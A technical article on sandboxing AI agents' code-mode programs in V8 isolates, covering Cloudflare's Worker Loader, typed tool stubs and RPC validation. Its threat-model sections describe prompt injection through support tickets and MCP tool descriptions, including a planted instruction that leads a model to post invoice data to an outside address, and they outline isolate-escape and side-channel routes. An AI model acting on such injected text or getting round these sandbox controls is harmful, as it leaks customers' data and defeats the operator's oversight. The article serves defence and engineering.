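# Running LLM-written code in V8 isolates: isolation, typed tool functions and sandbox escape

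## What a V8 isolate is, and why agents' code is run in one

A V8 isolate is a single instance of V8, the engine Google makes for its Chrome browser. V8 runs JavaScript and WebAssembly, a compact binary format to which languages such as C++ and Rust compile. Each isolate has its own memory for objects and its own copy of JavaScript's built-in functions. Node.js and Deno, which run JavaScript outside a browser, also use V8, as does Cloudflare Workers, a service that runs customers' code in Cloudflare's data centres.

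Since 2025, isolates have also been used to run code written by AI agents. An AI agent is a language model connected to software functions that let it act, such as by looking up records or sending messages. Many agents now act by writing a short program that calls several of these functions. The program usually runs seconds after the model writes it, before anyone has read it. An isolate is one option for running it, because an isolate starts in milliseconds and the code inside can reach only the functions provided by the host, the trusted program around it. The isolate, the host's controls and any further barriers around them make up the sandbox.

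### Which of these things share memory

JavaScript programs keep nearly everything they create, including strings, arrays and functions, in a region of memory called the heap. In *Heaps of Built-ins*, written for the security company Endor Labs, Haynes (2026) explains that what a script can do to other scripts depends on what it can reach on the heap. Two scripts on one heap can hold references to each other's objects, and from any object a script can follow links to everything connected with it. They may also share the built-ins, objects such as `Array` and `Function` that exist before any script runs, and JavaScript lets scripts alter these. For example, a hostile script can replace the shared function that arrays use for mapping, so that a trusted script runs the hostile code the next time it maps over an array.

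V8 can separate code inside a process with contexts or, more strongly, with isolates. A context is a set of global objects inside an isolate. Two contexts have different `Array` objects, so the replacement trick fails, but they still share a heap. If the host passes one of its own objects into the second context, code there may be able to follow the object's links back to the host's `Function`, which turns a string into a function on the host's side. The Node.js library vm2 tried to guard that kind of path with wrappers written in JavaScript, but Haynes counts more than twenty documented escapes from it. A separate isolate removes the path because it has its own heap. No reference leads from one heap to the other, and values cross only when the host copies them.

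An isolate provides weaker isolation than a process, the operating system's unit for a running program. Each process has its own range of memory addresses, and the processor, controlled by the operating system's kernel, stops one process from reading another's memory. Isolates often share a process, so their heaps lie in the same range of addresses and their separation depends on V8 working correctly. Containers and virtual machines are larger units than processes. A container is a group of processes to which the Linux kernel shows a private view of files and network. A virtual machine is a software imitation of a whole computer, with its own kernel.

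| Unit | Has to itself | Shares with its neighbours |
|---|---|---|
| Context | Global objects and built-ins | The isolate's heap, the process, the kernel |
| Isolate | Heap, garbage collector and built-ins | Often the process and its memory addresses; the kernel |
| Process | Memory addresses | The kernel |
| Container | View of files, network and processes | The kernel |
| Virtual machine | Kernel and a block of the machine's memory | The physical machine and the hypervisor, the software that divides it up |

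Chrome puts isolates inside separate processes. Cloudflare mostly does not, because of the cost, discussed below. Cloudflare engineers Varda, Pai and Gupta write in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, and that anyone running possibly malicious code in isolates needs further layers of defence around them.

### From tool calls to code mode

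A language model produces text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, so it needs a convention for taking actions. In an ordinary tool call, the developer puts a description of each available function into the model's input. To call a function, the model emits a special marker that corresponds to no text, a short message with the function's name and arguments, and a closing marker. The message is in JSON, a format for structured data. The harness, the program that runs the model, then pauses generation. The agent's software carries out the call, the harness feeds the result back between markers of its own, and the model continues. Varda and Pai add in *Code Mode*, the September 2025 post that named the newer technique, that models learn these markers from synthetic examples but are trained on real code from millions of projects.

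The Model Context Protocol (MCP) standardises how agents connect to tools. A company that wants agents to use its service runs an MCP server, which lists documented tools and accepts calls to them. The agent's client connects to the server and fetches the list, and authorisation happens outside the model's text. An agent can therefore use a server whose developers know nothing about that agent. Anthropic launched the protocol in November 2024, and developers have since built thousands of MCP servers.

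When an agent has many tools, their descriptions and intermediate results take up much of the model's input. In an example from Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, an agent fetches a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attaches it to a customer record in Salesforce. The model has to read the whole transcript and then write it out again as an argument to the second call, and it may make mistakes in copying it.

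Code mode gives the model a programming interface to write against and a single tool that runs the program it writes. Suppose a support agent has to find the open tickets that come from customers with unpaid invoices. The host fetches the tool descriptions from the ticket server and the billing server and turns them into declarations in TypeScript, which is JavaScript with notes on what type each value has:

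```typescript
declare const tickets: {
  /** Open support tickets, newest first. */
  listOpen(limit: number): Promise<Ticket[]>;
};
declare const billing: {
  /** Unpaid invoices of one customer. */
  overdue(customerId: string): Promise<Invoice[]>;
};
```

The declarations go into the model's input, and the model answers with a program:

```typescript
const hits = [];
for (const t of await tickets.listOpen(200)) {
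  const unpaid = await billing.overdue(t.customerId);
  if (unpaid.length > 0) hits.push({ ticket: t.id, unpaid: unpaid.length });
}
return hits;
```

The host strips out any type annotations, since V8 runs plain JavaScript, and loads the program into a new isolate. The program can call `tickets.listOpen` and `billing.overdue` like local functions, but each is a typed stub that sends a copy of its arguments to the host. The host adds the access token the service requires, contacts the right MCP server and sends a copy of the answer back to the isolate. If there are two hundred open tickets, the program makes 201 calls without involving the model: one to list the tickets and one billing check for each. When the program finishes, the host passes its return value or printed output to the model and discards the isolate.

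This saves tokens. In *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026) tested 14 models, and for 11 of them it was at least as accurate as ordinary tool calls. When a catalogue is large, even the declarations grow long, so Anthropic's version puts them in files that the model opens as needed. The *Code mode* documentation for OpenClaw, an agent program, describes a similar design. The model starts with two tools, one to run code and one to resume a paused run, and its code searches a hidden catalogue for the rest.

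By default, only the final result returns to the model, but the program can override this. If the model had written a line returning every ticket, all two hundred would have entered its input. Ronacher (2026), in *What is Codemode*, reports that agents commonly fetch five or ten items to learn how the data is structured, then write a program for the rest. Ronacher, who works on the coding agent Pi, also notes that an agent's shell commands may run on a separate machine that is already confined, while code-mode programs run on the harness's side, in their own sandbox, because they need tools that only the harness can supply. A weak sandbox there exposes the trusted side of the system.

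An application could run an agent's program directly with JavaScript's `eval` function, but the code would then have the same access as the application, including to its secrets and internal services, as Kapoor (2026) warns in *Introducing Run SDK*, an announcement from the hosting company Vercel. A container would prevent this, but because containers are slower to start, developers may reuse one for several tasks, leaving traces of one task for the next. An isolate starts quickly enough to be created for a single program and then discarded. Cloudflare said in March 2026 that isolates start about a hundred times faster than containers, but that was before it rebuilt its own containers in September to start six times faster (Cloudflare, 2026).

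An isolate also starts with little beyond the JavaScript language itself, which has no functions for opening files or network connections. Browsers and Node.js add those functions, but a host can leave them out. Each object or function the host does supply is a capability, meaning that any code that holds it may use it. The support agent's program can look up unpaid invoices because it has `billing.overdue`. It can't issue refunds, because it has neither a function for that nor general network access to send a refund request itself.

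### How hosting and agents came together

Cloudflare's Workers service has run on isolates since it launched in about 2018. *Mitigating Spectre and Other Security Threats* (Cloudflare, 2020) explains why. Cloudflare made the code of every tenant (a customer whose code and data share a machine with other customers') available in each of about 200 locations, many of them small. A machine had to hold thousands of tenants and switch among them thousands of times a second. Giving each tenant its own process could have raised processor use tenfold, so Cloudflare put many isolates in one process and added an outer sandbox that blocks the whole process from accessing files and the network.

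*Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024) proposed that agents act by writing code. In its framework, CodeAct, the model writes Python, an interpreter runs it, and the model revises its next step using the output. Cloudflare's *Codemode* documentation credits the paper as the inspiration for Codemode, although the paper doesn't involve V8.

Varda and Pai combined the two lines of work in September 2025. Until then, customers had to upload Worker code to Cloudflare ahead of time for deployment around the world. The new Worker Loader interface let one Worker create another on demand from a string of text, which is what an agent needs. Anthropic's post followed on 4 November 2025 (Willison, 2025, *Code execution with MCP*). It cited Cloudflare's findings and reached the same conclusion about writing code against MCP servers, but left the choice of sandbox open. Anthropic also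 considered it a drawback that the method needs sandboxing, resource limits and monitoring, which direct tool calls do not.

Cloudflare now calls a Worker created this way a Dynamic Worker. The feature entered open beta on 24 March 2026 for all customers on a paid Workers plan (Cloudflare, *Dynamic Workers, now in open beta*, 2026). It seems not to have reached general release by early December, though Cloudflare has published billing rules and keeps usage figures from 1 June onward. Cloudflare still warns that the accompanying code-mode package is experimental and may introduce breaking changes.

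Other companies also run agent code on V8. OpenAI starts a fresh, isolated V8 runtime for each program a model writes, without Node.js, package installation or direct network access, according to its *Programmatic Tool Calling* documentation. OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a code mode that runs JavaScript in Deno, according to OpenClaw. Developers who host their own agents can use isolated-vm, an open-source package that lets a Node.js program create isolates and load code into them. Mastra, an agent framework, uses it to run tool-calling programs that models write, and several automation products use it to run scripts that people write.

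Code mode can also run on JavaScript engines other than V8. Pi, OpenClaw and Vercel's Run SDK all use QuickJS, a much smaller engine, and Pi and OpenClaw run it inside WebAssembly. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, gained an experimental JavaScript code mode in November 2026 (InfoQ, *Claude Code Adds Experimental Code Mode to Orchestrate Tool Calls with JavaScript*, 2026). Patel and colleagues still describe JSON tool calls as the dominant interface in deployed agents.

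### What the sandbox has to withstand

Agent code can be harmful for several reasons. The most ordinary is a mistake by the model, such as writing a loop that never ends or leaving a filter blank so that a deletion meant for one record applies to all of them.

The second source of trouble is prompt injection, in which text in the data a model reads makes it follow an outsider's instructions. For example, a stranger might write a support ticket telling any AI that reads it to mark the account's invoices as paid. A model that samples ten tickets before writing its program may carry that request into the code. Akamai, another hosting company, warns buyers of its own agent sandbox that instructions from the developer do not reliably prevent this, since a model may ignore them or follow text buried in what it reads. Code mode reduces the risk somewhat, because data that stays in the isolate never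 reaches the model. But the model still reads the tool descriptions, and the operator of an MCP server could put instructions in those.

A hostile user can attack without hidden text. Anyone with an account on a public agent service can ask the agent to write a malicious program, or paste one in and ask the agent to run it. Varda and colleagues treat this as trivially easy.

A host cannot reliably tell these cases apart by inspecting the program, so it is safest to treat every program as if an attacker wrote it. OpenClaw explicitly classes all model-written code as hostile. The attacker is assumed to be able to choose every character of the program, run many variants repeatedly, and study V8, whose source code is public and whose security fixes become available to attackers and defenders at the same time. The host's code, the operating system and the hardware are treated as trusted, though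 any of them may contain bugs.

Five things need protection. The first is the host process, because code that gained control of it could do whatever the host can, and a Dynamic Worker usually runs on the same thread as the Worker that created it. Other tenants' code and data, which may be in the same process, also need protection, as do credentials. Varda and Pai argue that a model cannot write code that leaks keys if the host holds them and adds them to each outgoing request. This is true if the program can only use well-written stubs, but not if it can read the memory that holds a key or if a badly written stub returns one.

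The services behind the tools need protecting even when the isolate works perfectly, because agent code can use them to make real changes, such as issuing a refund or deleting a record. The last item is the cost of running agent code, which uses processor time and makes paid calls. In Pi, those can include calls to image generators and other AI models, so a careless loop can run up charges quickly.

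The arrangement can fail these five in four ways:

- Misuse of permitted functions: the program stays inside the isolate and calls only its stubs, but does harm with them, for instance by copying private tickets into an outgoing message.
- Exhaustion of resources: the program runs without end, fills memory or makes so many calls that the host stalls, other tenants slow down or the bill climbs.
- Escape: the program gains access to memory or functions outside the isolate that the host never gave it, through a fault in V8 or in the library that connects the isolate to the host.
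- Leakage through side channels: the program reads no forbidden memory directly and infers secrets from effects such as how long an operation takes.

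## Loading the code with nothing but what it is given

The host receives a model's program as text and, before running it, has to turn it into something V8 can load and decide which functions and data it can access. This section uses Cloudflare's Worker Loader to show the whole procedure, with the support agent's program as the example.

### From the model's text to a module

Models may return a program inside Markdown code fences, as bare statements, or as a complete function. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode API reference*, the `normalizeCode` function in the company's code-mode package removes the fences and converts the common forms into a single async function. The support agent's program needs this conversion because it ends with `return hits;`. JavaScript permits `return` only inside a function, so V8 would reject the program as a module on its own.

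The host then puts the function into a small module. In simplified form:

```js
import { WorkerEntrypoint } from "cloudflare:workers";

export default class extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async run() {
    const { tickets, billing } = this.env;
    const program = async () => { /* the model's code */ };
    return await program();
  }
}
```

This wrapper runs inside the isolate alongside the agent code, which could tamper with it. The wrapper can handle chores such as collecting printed output, but the host shouldn't keep secrets in it or rely on it to enforce rules.

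Type annotations have to be removed before the code is loaded, because the Worker Loader has no build step. Cloudflare's package avoids most of the problem by instructing the model to write plain JavaScript, even though the declarations it is given are in TypeScript.

If the program uses libraries, the host has to supply those too. Cloudflare's bundler takes source files and a list of dependencies, downloads the packages from the npm registry, compiles any TypeScript and returns a set of modules. It runs on the host's side before the isolate exists, so if the model writes the dependency list, the model chooses what the trusted side downloads. It is safer to supply a fixed set of libraries, which the code-mode package accepts through its `modules` option. Inside the isolate, a library has the same access as the agent code and can't expand it.

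### The fields of the Worker Loader

The host Worker gets the loader from a line in its configuration and calls it like this:

```js
const worker = env.LOADER.load({
  compatibilityDate: "2026-10-14",
  mainModule: "main.js",
  modules: { "main.js": wrappedProgram },
  env: { tickets: ticketStub, billing: billingStub },
  globalOutbound: null,
});
const result = await worker.getEntrypoint().run();
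```

According to Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers* documentation, `modules` maps file names to their contents, which can be JavaScript, Python, text, JSON, binary data or compiled WebAssembly, and `mainModule` names the module to start from. The program can import only these modules and the ones built into Cloudflare's runtime. Cloudflare recommends JavaScript for one-off programs because Python takes much longer to start.

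`compatibilityDate` selects a version of the runtime's behaviour. Cloudflare sometimes makes changes that would break older code, and a Worker with an earlier date keeps the earlier behaviour. A separate list of compatibility flags turns on individual features, including Python. Since a later date or an extra flag can add functions to the sandbox, it makes sense to set a fixed date in the host's code and review the changes before moving to a later one.

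`env` holds what the host gives the program. It can contain plain data, which the loader copies into the isolate, and service bindings, which arrive as stubs whose methods run in the host. Credentials belong behind a stub because the program can read any string in `env`. Agent code can't forge a stub for another service, so it can only call services whose stubs it has been given. The support agent's program is given two stubs.

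`globalOutbound` controls the program's network access. If the host omits it, the Dynamic Worker inherits the host's own access, usually to the whole public internet. Setting it to `null` blocks network access. The host can also supply a service binding, which sends every outgoing request to a host function that can inspect it or add credentials. Cloudflare's code-mode package sets the field to `null` by default, but the underlying loader does not. One Cloudflare example, which shows how to bundle a library, omits the field, so a developer who copied it to run agent code would give that code the host's network access.

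A spelling mistake could have the same effect. Developers who had tried the loader for their own platform reported in Lumenize's *Running untrusted code on Cloudflare* that it silently ignored properties it didn't recognise. If that still holds, a host that sets `globalOutbund` to `null` gets no error, and the program it loads can still reach the internet. TypeScript's checks on the host's code should catch this, and so should a test that checks that a loaded program's attempt to reach the internet fails.

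### What happens when the program calls `fetch()`

Suppose a customer's ticket contains a hidden instruction, and the model adds a line that uses `fetch()` to post the list of unpaid invoices to an outside address. `fetch()` still exists, because Cloudflare's runtime defines it in every Worker, but with `globalOutbound` set to `null`, calling it throws an exception and no request is sent. `connect()`, which opens lower-level network connections, is blocked in the same way.

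If the program doesn't catch the exception, it stops, and the code-mode package returns the error to the model, which may write another program. If the program catches the exception, it can keep running and using its stubs, since the host makes their network requests.

The code can't do anything it hasn't been given a function for, just as the support agent can't issue refunds. A program in an ordinary container, by contrast, starts with files, environment variables (where developers often keep keys) and usually network access, and the operator writes rules to take some of that away. Varda and Pai point out that on most platforms a program needs general network access to reach even one private service, whereas a binding lets it reach the service directly.

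I would put more weight on how the two approaches fail. When an operator forgets a rule, the permission stays in place and everything appears to work, but when a host forgets a stub, somebody notices because the program can't do its job. By that test the Worker Loader handles `env` well, since the code receives only what the host passes in, and handles the network badly, since access stays on unless the host blocks it.

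Cloudflare concedes that blocking `fetch()` may not be feasible for code that depends on existing libraries, because many of them expect to make HTTP requests. Starting with nothing also doesn't protect against a stub that is too powerful.

### What bare JavaScript still offers

Code in an isolate with no stubs and no network can still compute, fill memory, read the clock, generate new code and, unless the host prevents it, run WebAssembly. The host can cap computation and memory but can't remove them, because every program needs both.

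Code that a program generates with `eval` or `Function` runs in the same isolate with the same stubs, so it has no more access than the program itself. But it defeats any check that relies on reading the program beforehand. V8 has a per-context setting that makes both throw an error. Deleting the two names isn't enough, because a program can still reach `Function` through any function's link to its constructor. Cloudflare disables `eval` and `Function` while a Worker is handling a request.

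V8 also lets the host block WebAssembly compilation. Few tool-calling programs need WebAssembly, and blocking it puts a large, complicated part of the engine out of an attacker's reach. In Workers, agent code can't compile WebAssembly from raw bytes during a request; the host has to supply the module when it loads the code.

Every Worker also receives some globals without importing them, including `console`, cryptographic functions and a cache for HTTP responses, according to documentation for Cloudflare's runtime hosted by Mintlify. These globals deserve the same review as the stubs, particularly the cache, because it is meant to keep data after a request ends.

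### The result is a way out

In the first version of code mode, the program returned its results by printing them with `console.log()`. The current package returns a result, any console output and any error message to the host, and Cloudflare passes all of these to the model.

Even with `fetch()` blocked and no other network access, a program can still send data out through what it returns or prints. That output enters the model's context, and from there it may reach the user, the company running the model or another tool. If the support agent can send email through an ordinary tool call, a program could return a private ticket and the model could email it to someone.

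Returned data can also contain a prompt injection, and even an error message can include text from the ticket that contains the injection. The host should treat the result, the printed output and the error as untrusted text.

Cloudflare offers two ways to change what the model receives. A function called `truncateResult` cuts long results, by default at an estimated 6,000 tokens, or about 24,000 characters. This saves money but leaves any sensitive data in the part it keeps. A hook called `transformResult` lets the host rewrite a completed result before the model sees it. According to Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works*, the runtime tries to record the original first, for auditing. The hook receives only the result, not what the program printed, so a host that uses it to remove customers' email addresses has to handle any addresses in the printed output separately.

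For support agents, I think it is better to return a narrow result in a known shape. The host could reject anything except a list of ticket numbers and counts, and keep the console output for developers. The drawback is that the model would lose some ability to debug its own programs, and reading errors and trying again is a large part of how agents get code to work.

### Discarding the isolate or keeping it

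`load()` creates a new Dynamic Worker on every call. The loader's other method, `get()`, takes an identifier and may return an isolate that is already running with that identifier. Cloudflare recommends `load()` for one-off agent programs and `get()` for applications that receive many requests.

Reusing a small isolate saves little time. In Lumenize's tests, creating one took a median of 1 millisecond, and calling one that was already running took less. Reuse saves more when the code includes large libraries. For example, a program with a 500-kilobyte module took 8 milliseconds to load. The tests ran on a developer's machine, so production times will differ.

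Reusing a Worker saves on fees. Cloudflare charges $0.002 for each distinct Dynamic Worker per day after the first thousand in a month, and every `load()` counts as a new one. Running ten thousand one-off programs in a day would cost about $20, plus processor time and requests. Ten thousand calls to one program under a stable identifier would count as only one Worker. Varda and colleagues argue that the fee is typically negligible compared with the cost of having a model write the code, which seems right for programs that run only once.

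Reusing an isolate risks carrying state from one run to the next. Top-level module variables survive, so a program that saves a customer's tickets in one may expose them to later code in the same isolate. Changes to shared built-ins also survive, so tampering with one can affect every later run.

A subtler leak can occur when the host uses a hash of the source as the isolate's identifier. If two customers' agents write exactly the same program, the second customer's request may reach the isolate made for the first, with the first customer's billing stub still in `env`. Cloudflare tells developers to change the identifier whenever the code or its configuration changes. For agent code, that configuration has to include whose data the stubs can reach.

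Other designs reuse the parts that are slow to start and replace only the program's memory. OpenClaw keeps worker threads warm but creates a new QuickJS virtual machine for each run or resumption.

Because each run starts in a fresh isolate, the host has to store anything that must outlast the run. When a program in Cloudflare's code mode reaches a call that needs a person's approval, the runtime ends that run. After approval, it runs the same source from the beginning in another isolate, taking the results of earlier calls from a log so that it doesn't repeat their effects. This works only if the program makes the same calls in the same order. A program that branches on the time or a random number may make different calls, in which case the runtime stops it with an error.

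A fresh isolate also does not undo changes the program made outside its previous isolate. Cloudflare has a package that gives agent code a virtual file system whose contents persist between runs. If two tasks share one of these file systems, the second can read an instruction planted by the first, even when it runs in a new isolate.

### Starting from less with isolated-vm

A new context in isolated-vm has JavaScript's own built-ins but nothing from Node.js. It doesn't define `console`, timers, `require` or `fetch`, even as stubs that throw errors. Standard Agent Spec's *Code Execution* describes a similar contract for agents, in which the caller must pass in even `console` and `fetch`.

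The host has to do by hand much of what the Worker Loader does from its configuration fields. It creates an isolate with a memory limit, creates a context inside it and attaches each function the program may call. The host then compiles the program, runs it with a timeout, copies out the result and disposes of the isolate. The program has no network access unless the host builds it, so forgetting a network setting can't open the network here.

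The danger then lies in the functions the host attaches. In the README, isolated-vm's maintainers warn developers never to let untrusted code get hold of the library's objects, such as a `Reference`, a handle to a value in another isolate. An attacker can usually use one to get back into the Node.js isolate and take control of the process. The maintainers also tell developers to install Node.js updates that contain V8 fixes and to run isolated-vm in a separate process from anything critical.

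## Writing the typed functions the code may call

Suppose the support agent must now tell paying customers that engineers have fixed a fault they reported. The host gives it three typed stubs. `tickets.search` finds tickets, `customers.get` looks up one customer, and `mail.send` sends an email from the company's support address.

### From JSON Schema to TypeScript

An MCP server describes each tool with a name, a short description and a JSON Schema, a document that defines what a valid input looks like. The ticket server's entry for its search tool might be:

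```json
{
  "name": "search",
  "description": "Search support tickets.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "query": { "type": "string", "description": "Words to look for" },
      "status": { "enum": ["open", "closed"] },
      "limit": { "type": "integer", "maximum": 50,
                 "description": "How many to return, at most 50" }
    },
    "required": ["query"]
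  }
}
```

The host turns this entry, and those for the other two tools, into declarations for the model to read:

```typescript
type Ticket = { id: string; customerId: string; subject: string; body: string };
type Customer = { id: string; name: string; email: string; plan: "free" | "paid" };

declare const tickets: {
  /** Search support tickets. */
  search(input: {
    /** Words to look for */
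    query: string;
    status?: "open" | "closed";
    /** How many to return, at most 50 */
    limit?: number;
  }): Promise<Ticket[]>;
};
declare const customers: {
  /** Look up one customer. */
  get(input: { id: string }): Promise<Customer>;
};
declare const mail: {
  /** Send an email from the support address. */
  send(input: {
    /** @format email */
    to: string;
    subject: string;
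    body: string;
  }): Promise<{ messageId: string }>;
};
```

Descriptions become comments, a list of permitted values becomes a union of string literals, and any property missing from `required` is marked optional with a question mark. Some rules have no TypeScript equivalent. For example, the type `number` cannot specify a maximum, so the model sees the limit of 50 only because the ticket server's developer repeated it in the description.

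*feat(codemode): support AI SDK jsonSchema wrapper + production-harden schema converter* (mattzcarey, 2026), a change to Cloudflare's code-mode package, lists what else the conversion loses. A format such as "email" is kept only as a comment beside an ordinary string. Conditional rules, such as requiring one field when another is present, become `unknown`, TypeScript's type for a value that could be anything. The converter also uses `unknown` for schemas that refer to themselves, schemas nested 20 levels deep, and references to external URLs, which it doesn't follow for security reasons. In all these cases, the model gets a vaguer declaration and the converter raises no error.

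The converter also has to handle hostile text, because the descriptions come from whoever runs the MCP server. In TypeScript, `*/` ends a comment, so any text after it in a description could be parsed as code. The converter escapes those characters, but it has no defence against a description that contains harmful instructions for the model.

TypeScript describes functions compactly. Varda and colleagues define a chat room with three functions in a few lines of it, and their equivalent in OpenAPI, the usual format for describing web services, is several times as long. They also argue that writing a small TypeScript interface is safer than filtering HTTP requests to an existing service, because a filter must account for every header and parameter that could change a request's meaning, while a wrapper can include only the functions the host wants to allow. The company's mail service can probably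 also read the inbox and change forwarding rules, but the support agent can call only `send`.

### How a call reaches the service

Given those declarations, the model might write this program:

```javascript
const hits = await tickets.search({ query: "export fails", status: "open", limit: 50 });
const notified = [];
for (const t of hits) {
  const c = await customers.get({ id: t.customerId });
  if (c.plan !== "paid") continue;
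  await mail.send({
    to: c.email,
    subject: `Re: ${t.subject}`,
    body: `Hello ${c.name}, we have fixed the export fault. Please try again.`,
  });
  notified.push(t.id);
}
return { notified };
```

Each call travels to the host by remote procedure call (RPC), a technique that makes a message to another program look like an ordinary function call. In Cloudflare's package, according to its Cloudflare documentation, the object the program calls is a JavaScript `Proxy`, which intercepts any use of its properties. A call to `customers.get` then goes through these steps:

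1. The proxy converts the arguments to text and sends them, with the method's name, to a dispatcher on the host.
2. The dispatcher finds the host function with that name.
3. The host function checks the arguments.
4. It adds the access token for the user the agent is working for and contacts the customer service.
5. The host sends the result or an error back as text, and the program continues from its `await`.

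If the search finds one ticket, from a paying customer, six messages cross the boundary:

| Isolate to host | What the host does | Host to isolate |
|---|---|---|
| `tickets.search`, with `{"query":"export fails","status":"open","limit":50}` | Checks the input, adds the ticket server's token, runs the search | `[{"id":"t_104","customerId":"c_81",…}]` |
| `customers.get`, with `{"id":"c_81"}` | Checks the input, adds the customer service's token, fetches the record | `{"id":"c_81","name":"Ana","email":"ana@example.com","plan":"paid"}` |
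| `mail.send`, with `{"to":"ana@example.com",…}` | Checks the input, adds the mail service's token, sends the email | `{"messageId":"m_9"}` |

The host's side of `customers.get` could look like this. It uses Zod, a library that checks values while a program is running:

```typescript
const GetInput = z.object({ id: z.string().regex(/^c_\d+$/) });
const CustomerOutput = z.object({
  id: z.string(), name: z.string(), email: z.string(),
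  plan: z.enum(["free", "paid"]),
});

async function getCustomer(raw: unknown, session: Session) {
  const { id } = GetInput.parse(raw);
  const reply = await customerService.get(id, { token: session.customerToken });
  return CustomerOutput.parse(reply);
}
```

The `session` value comes from the host's own record of who is using the agent. If the function took the user's identity as an argument, the program could pass someone else's.

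Varda and colleagues call the bridge between the isolate and the host Cap'n Web, while Cloudflare's documentation calls it Workers RPC. Cloudflare also released a protocol called Cap'n Web for use between any two JavaScript programs. Cloudflare's *Cap'n Web* (2025) describes the protocol as similar to the RPC system in Workers.

In Cap'n Web, each side keeps a numbered table of the objects it has offered to the other. Entry 0 is its main interface. To make a call, one side sends a `push` message with an entry number, a method name and the arguments. The other side runs the method and stores the result under the next positive number. If the caller needs the value, it sends a `pull` message and gets back `resolve` with the value or `reject` with an error. Because the caller can predict the number of each result, it can use that number in a second call before the first has finished, so a chain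 of dependent calls can take a single round trip.

The table also makes a stub a capability, because a program that invents an entry number gets nothing unless the host has put an object at that entry.

Code can also pass objects with methods across the boundary this way, but each object stays on the side that created it. In Cloudflare's example, a login method checks a key and returns a session object, and only code that holds the session can call its methods. The support agent's host could likewise have `customers.get` return an object with a method for emailing that one customer, and remove `mail.send`. The code-mode package's dispatcher sends text, so a developer would have to give the isolate a direct binding to do this.

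Functions cross the isolate boundary in the same way, so when the host calls a callback it accepted from the program, the agent's code runs in the isolate while the host waits for the result. That result may contain false data or never arrive.

### What the types can't enforce

Type declarations help the model write the program, and the host can then use the TypeScript compiler to check the program against them before running it. The compiler can also check plain JavaScript.

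This check matters most for programs with side effects. Suppose the model adds a call to `tickets.close`, which doesn't exist, at the end of the loop that emails customers. The compiler would catch the mistake before any email is sent. Without the check, the first customer gets an email before the program fails, and a second when the model fixes the program and the host runs it again.

By the time V8 runs the program, the types are gone. Cloudflare warns in the Cap'n Web announcement that the RPC system does not stop a malicious caller from sending arguments of the wrong type. The compiler can't be relied on either, because TypeScript has casts, which tell it to treat a value as some other type:

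```typescript
await customers.get({ id: 123 as never });
```

The declaration requires a string, but `never` is a special type that TypeScript accepts wherever it expects any other, so this compiles. Once the host strips the types, V8 runs:

```javascript
await customers.get({ id: 123 });
```

The host receives `{"id":123}`. `GetInput.parse` throws an error because `id` is a number, not a string, so the program's call fails and the host never contacts the customer service. If the host skipped the compile check, an attacker wouldn't need the cast, since the second version is already valid JavaScript.

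Without the check, an object where the host expects a string can change the meaning of a database query, and a missing filter can make a query match every record. Other mistakes, such as a number in place of a customer ID, may do no harm.

Developers who use Cloudflare's package may not be getting this check. The Cloudflare API reference gives different behaviour for different ways of importing and wrapping tools:

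| Import path | Does its tool wrapper check arguments at run time? |
|---|---|
| `@cloudflare/codemode/ai` | Yes, where the tool's schema supports it |
| `@cloudflare/codemode` | No |
| `@cloudflare/codemode/tanstack-ai` | No |
| `@cloudflare/codemode/browser` | No, the schema only produces declarations |

The first three paths each export `resolveProvider`. A developer who changes the import line from the first path to the second loses the check, possibly without any visible sign. It is safer to validate inside each host function, as `getCustomer` does, regardless of what the surrounding package does.

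Developers can also generate the checks from the TypeScript types. The capnweb-validate package does this when a developer builds the host, according to its README in *capnweb-validate* on Pkg Stats, a JavaScript package index. The developer marks a class, and the build tool adds code that checks each incoming argument and throws a `TypeError` on a mismatch. If the build step doesn't run, the mark throws an error, so the service can't accidentally accept unchecked calls.

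The README also shows how a host can expose more than its developer intended. By default, the other side can call every public method of an RPC class, including helpers missing from the interface the class implements. Naming the interface in the mark restricts callers to its methods. Compiling to JavaScript removes TypeScript's `private` keyword along with the types, so a helper that has to stay hidden should have a name beginning with `#`, which JavaScript enforces as private.

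Generated checks can be no stricter than the types. Arguments typed `any` or `unknown` pass whatever they contain, and methods with several alternative signatures go unchecked, though the build gives a warning. The types also can't express the limit of 50 tickets, so the host has to check that separately.

Even perfect shape checking would let a program email one customer's ticket to another customer, because both the address and the text are valid strings. It also wouldn't protect against a memory bug in the code that copies values between the isolate and the host.

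### Vague output types

Developers tend to type inputs more carefully than outputs. In the first code-mode example that Varda and Pai published, generated from a real MCP server, every tool's output was typed as an object with any fields. Sample declarations in Cloudflare's later documentation return `Promise<unknown>`. Output schemas are optional, and when a server doesn't provide one, the converter can't generate a more specific type.

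The type `any` turns off type checking. If `tickets.search` returned `any`, the model could write `t.customer_id` instead of `t.customerId` and the program would compile. The misspelt field would be undefined, and `customers.get` would receive an object with no ID. With `unknown`, the compiler won't let the program read a field until the program has tested the value's type. But a cast bypasses this check and leaves the program no safer than with `any`.

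Vague output types also increase the risk of prompt injection, because a model that isn't given the structure of a ticket has to read a few to work it out, and their text can contain injected instructions. A precise output type removes one reason to read tickets.

That makes it worth writing output types by hand when the server doesn't supply them. Cloudflare's package accepts handwritten declarations in a field called `types`. These declarations can become outdated when the service changes, so the host should check results as well as arguments. The last line of `getCustomer` checks the result. By default, Zod drops any field the schema doesn't list, so if the service started returning card details, they would stay on the host.

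### Two functions for a very large API

Three declarations take up little of a model's input, but Cloudflare's own API has more than 2,500 endpoints, and describing them all would exceed the input limit of most models. The company's MCP server for this API therefore offers only two tools, `search` and `execute`. Each takes a short JavaScript program and runs it in a Dynamic Worker.

A `search` program receives the full OpenAPI description of the service as an object called `spec`. The model receives only what the program returns. An `execute` program gets a function called `cloudflare.request`, which takes an HTTP method and a path, and its calls are already authorised.

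Cloudflare demonstrates this with a user who wants to protect a website from denial-of-service attacks, which flood a site with traffic. The model's first program searches the description for paths related to firewalls and rule sets, and returns ten operations. The second reads the schema of one operation to find the permitted values of a field. The third lists the site's existing rule sets, and the fourth fetches the settings of two of them. The task takes four tool calls, and the model never reads the other 2,490 or so endpoints.

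The two-function design loses much of the benefit of typed functions. `cloudflare.request` accepts any path, so the compiler can't distinguish a correct request from an invented one. The design also hides the individual operations from the software around the model. In ordinary MCP, when the model requests a call to, say, `delete_record`, that software can ask the user for approval first. With the two-function design, it receives only a call to `execute` with a program.

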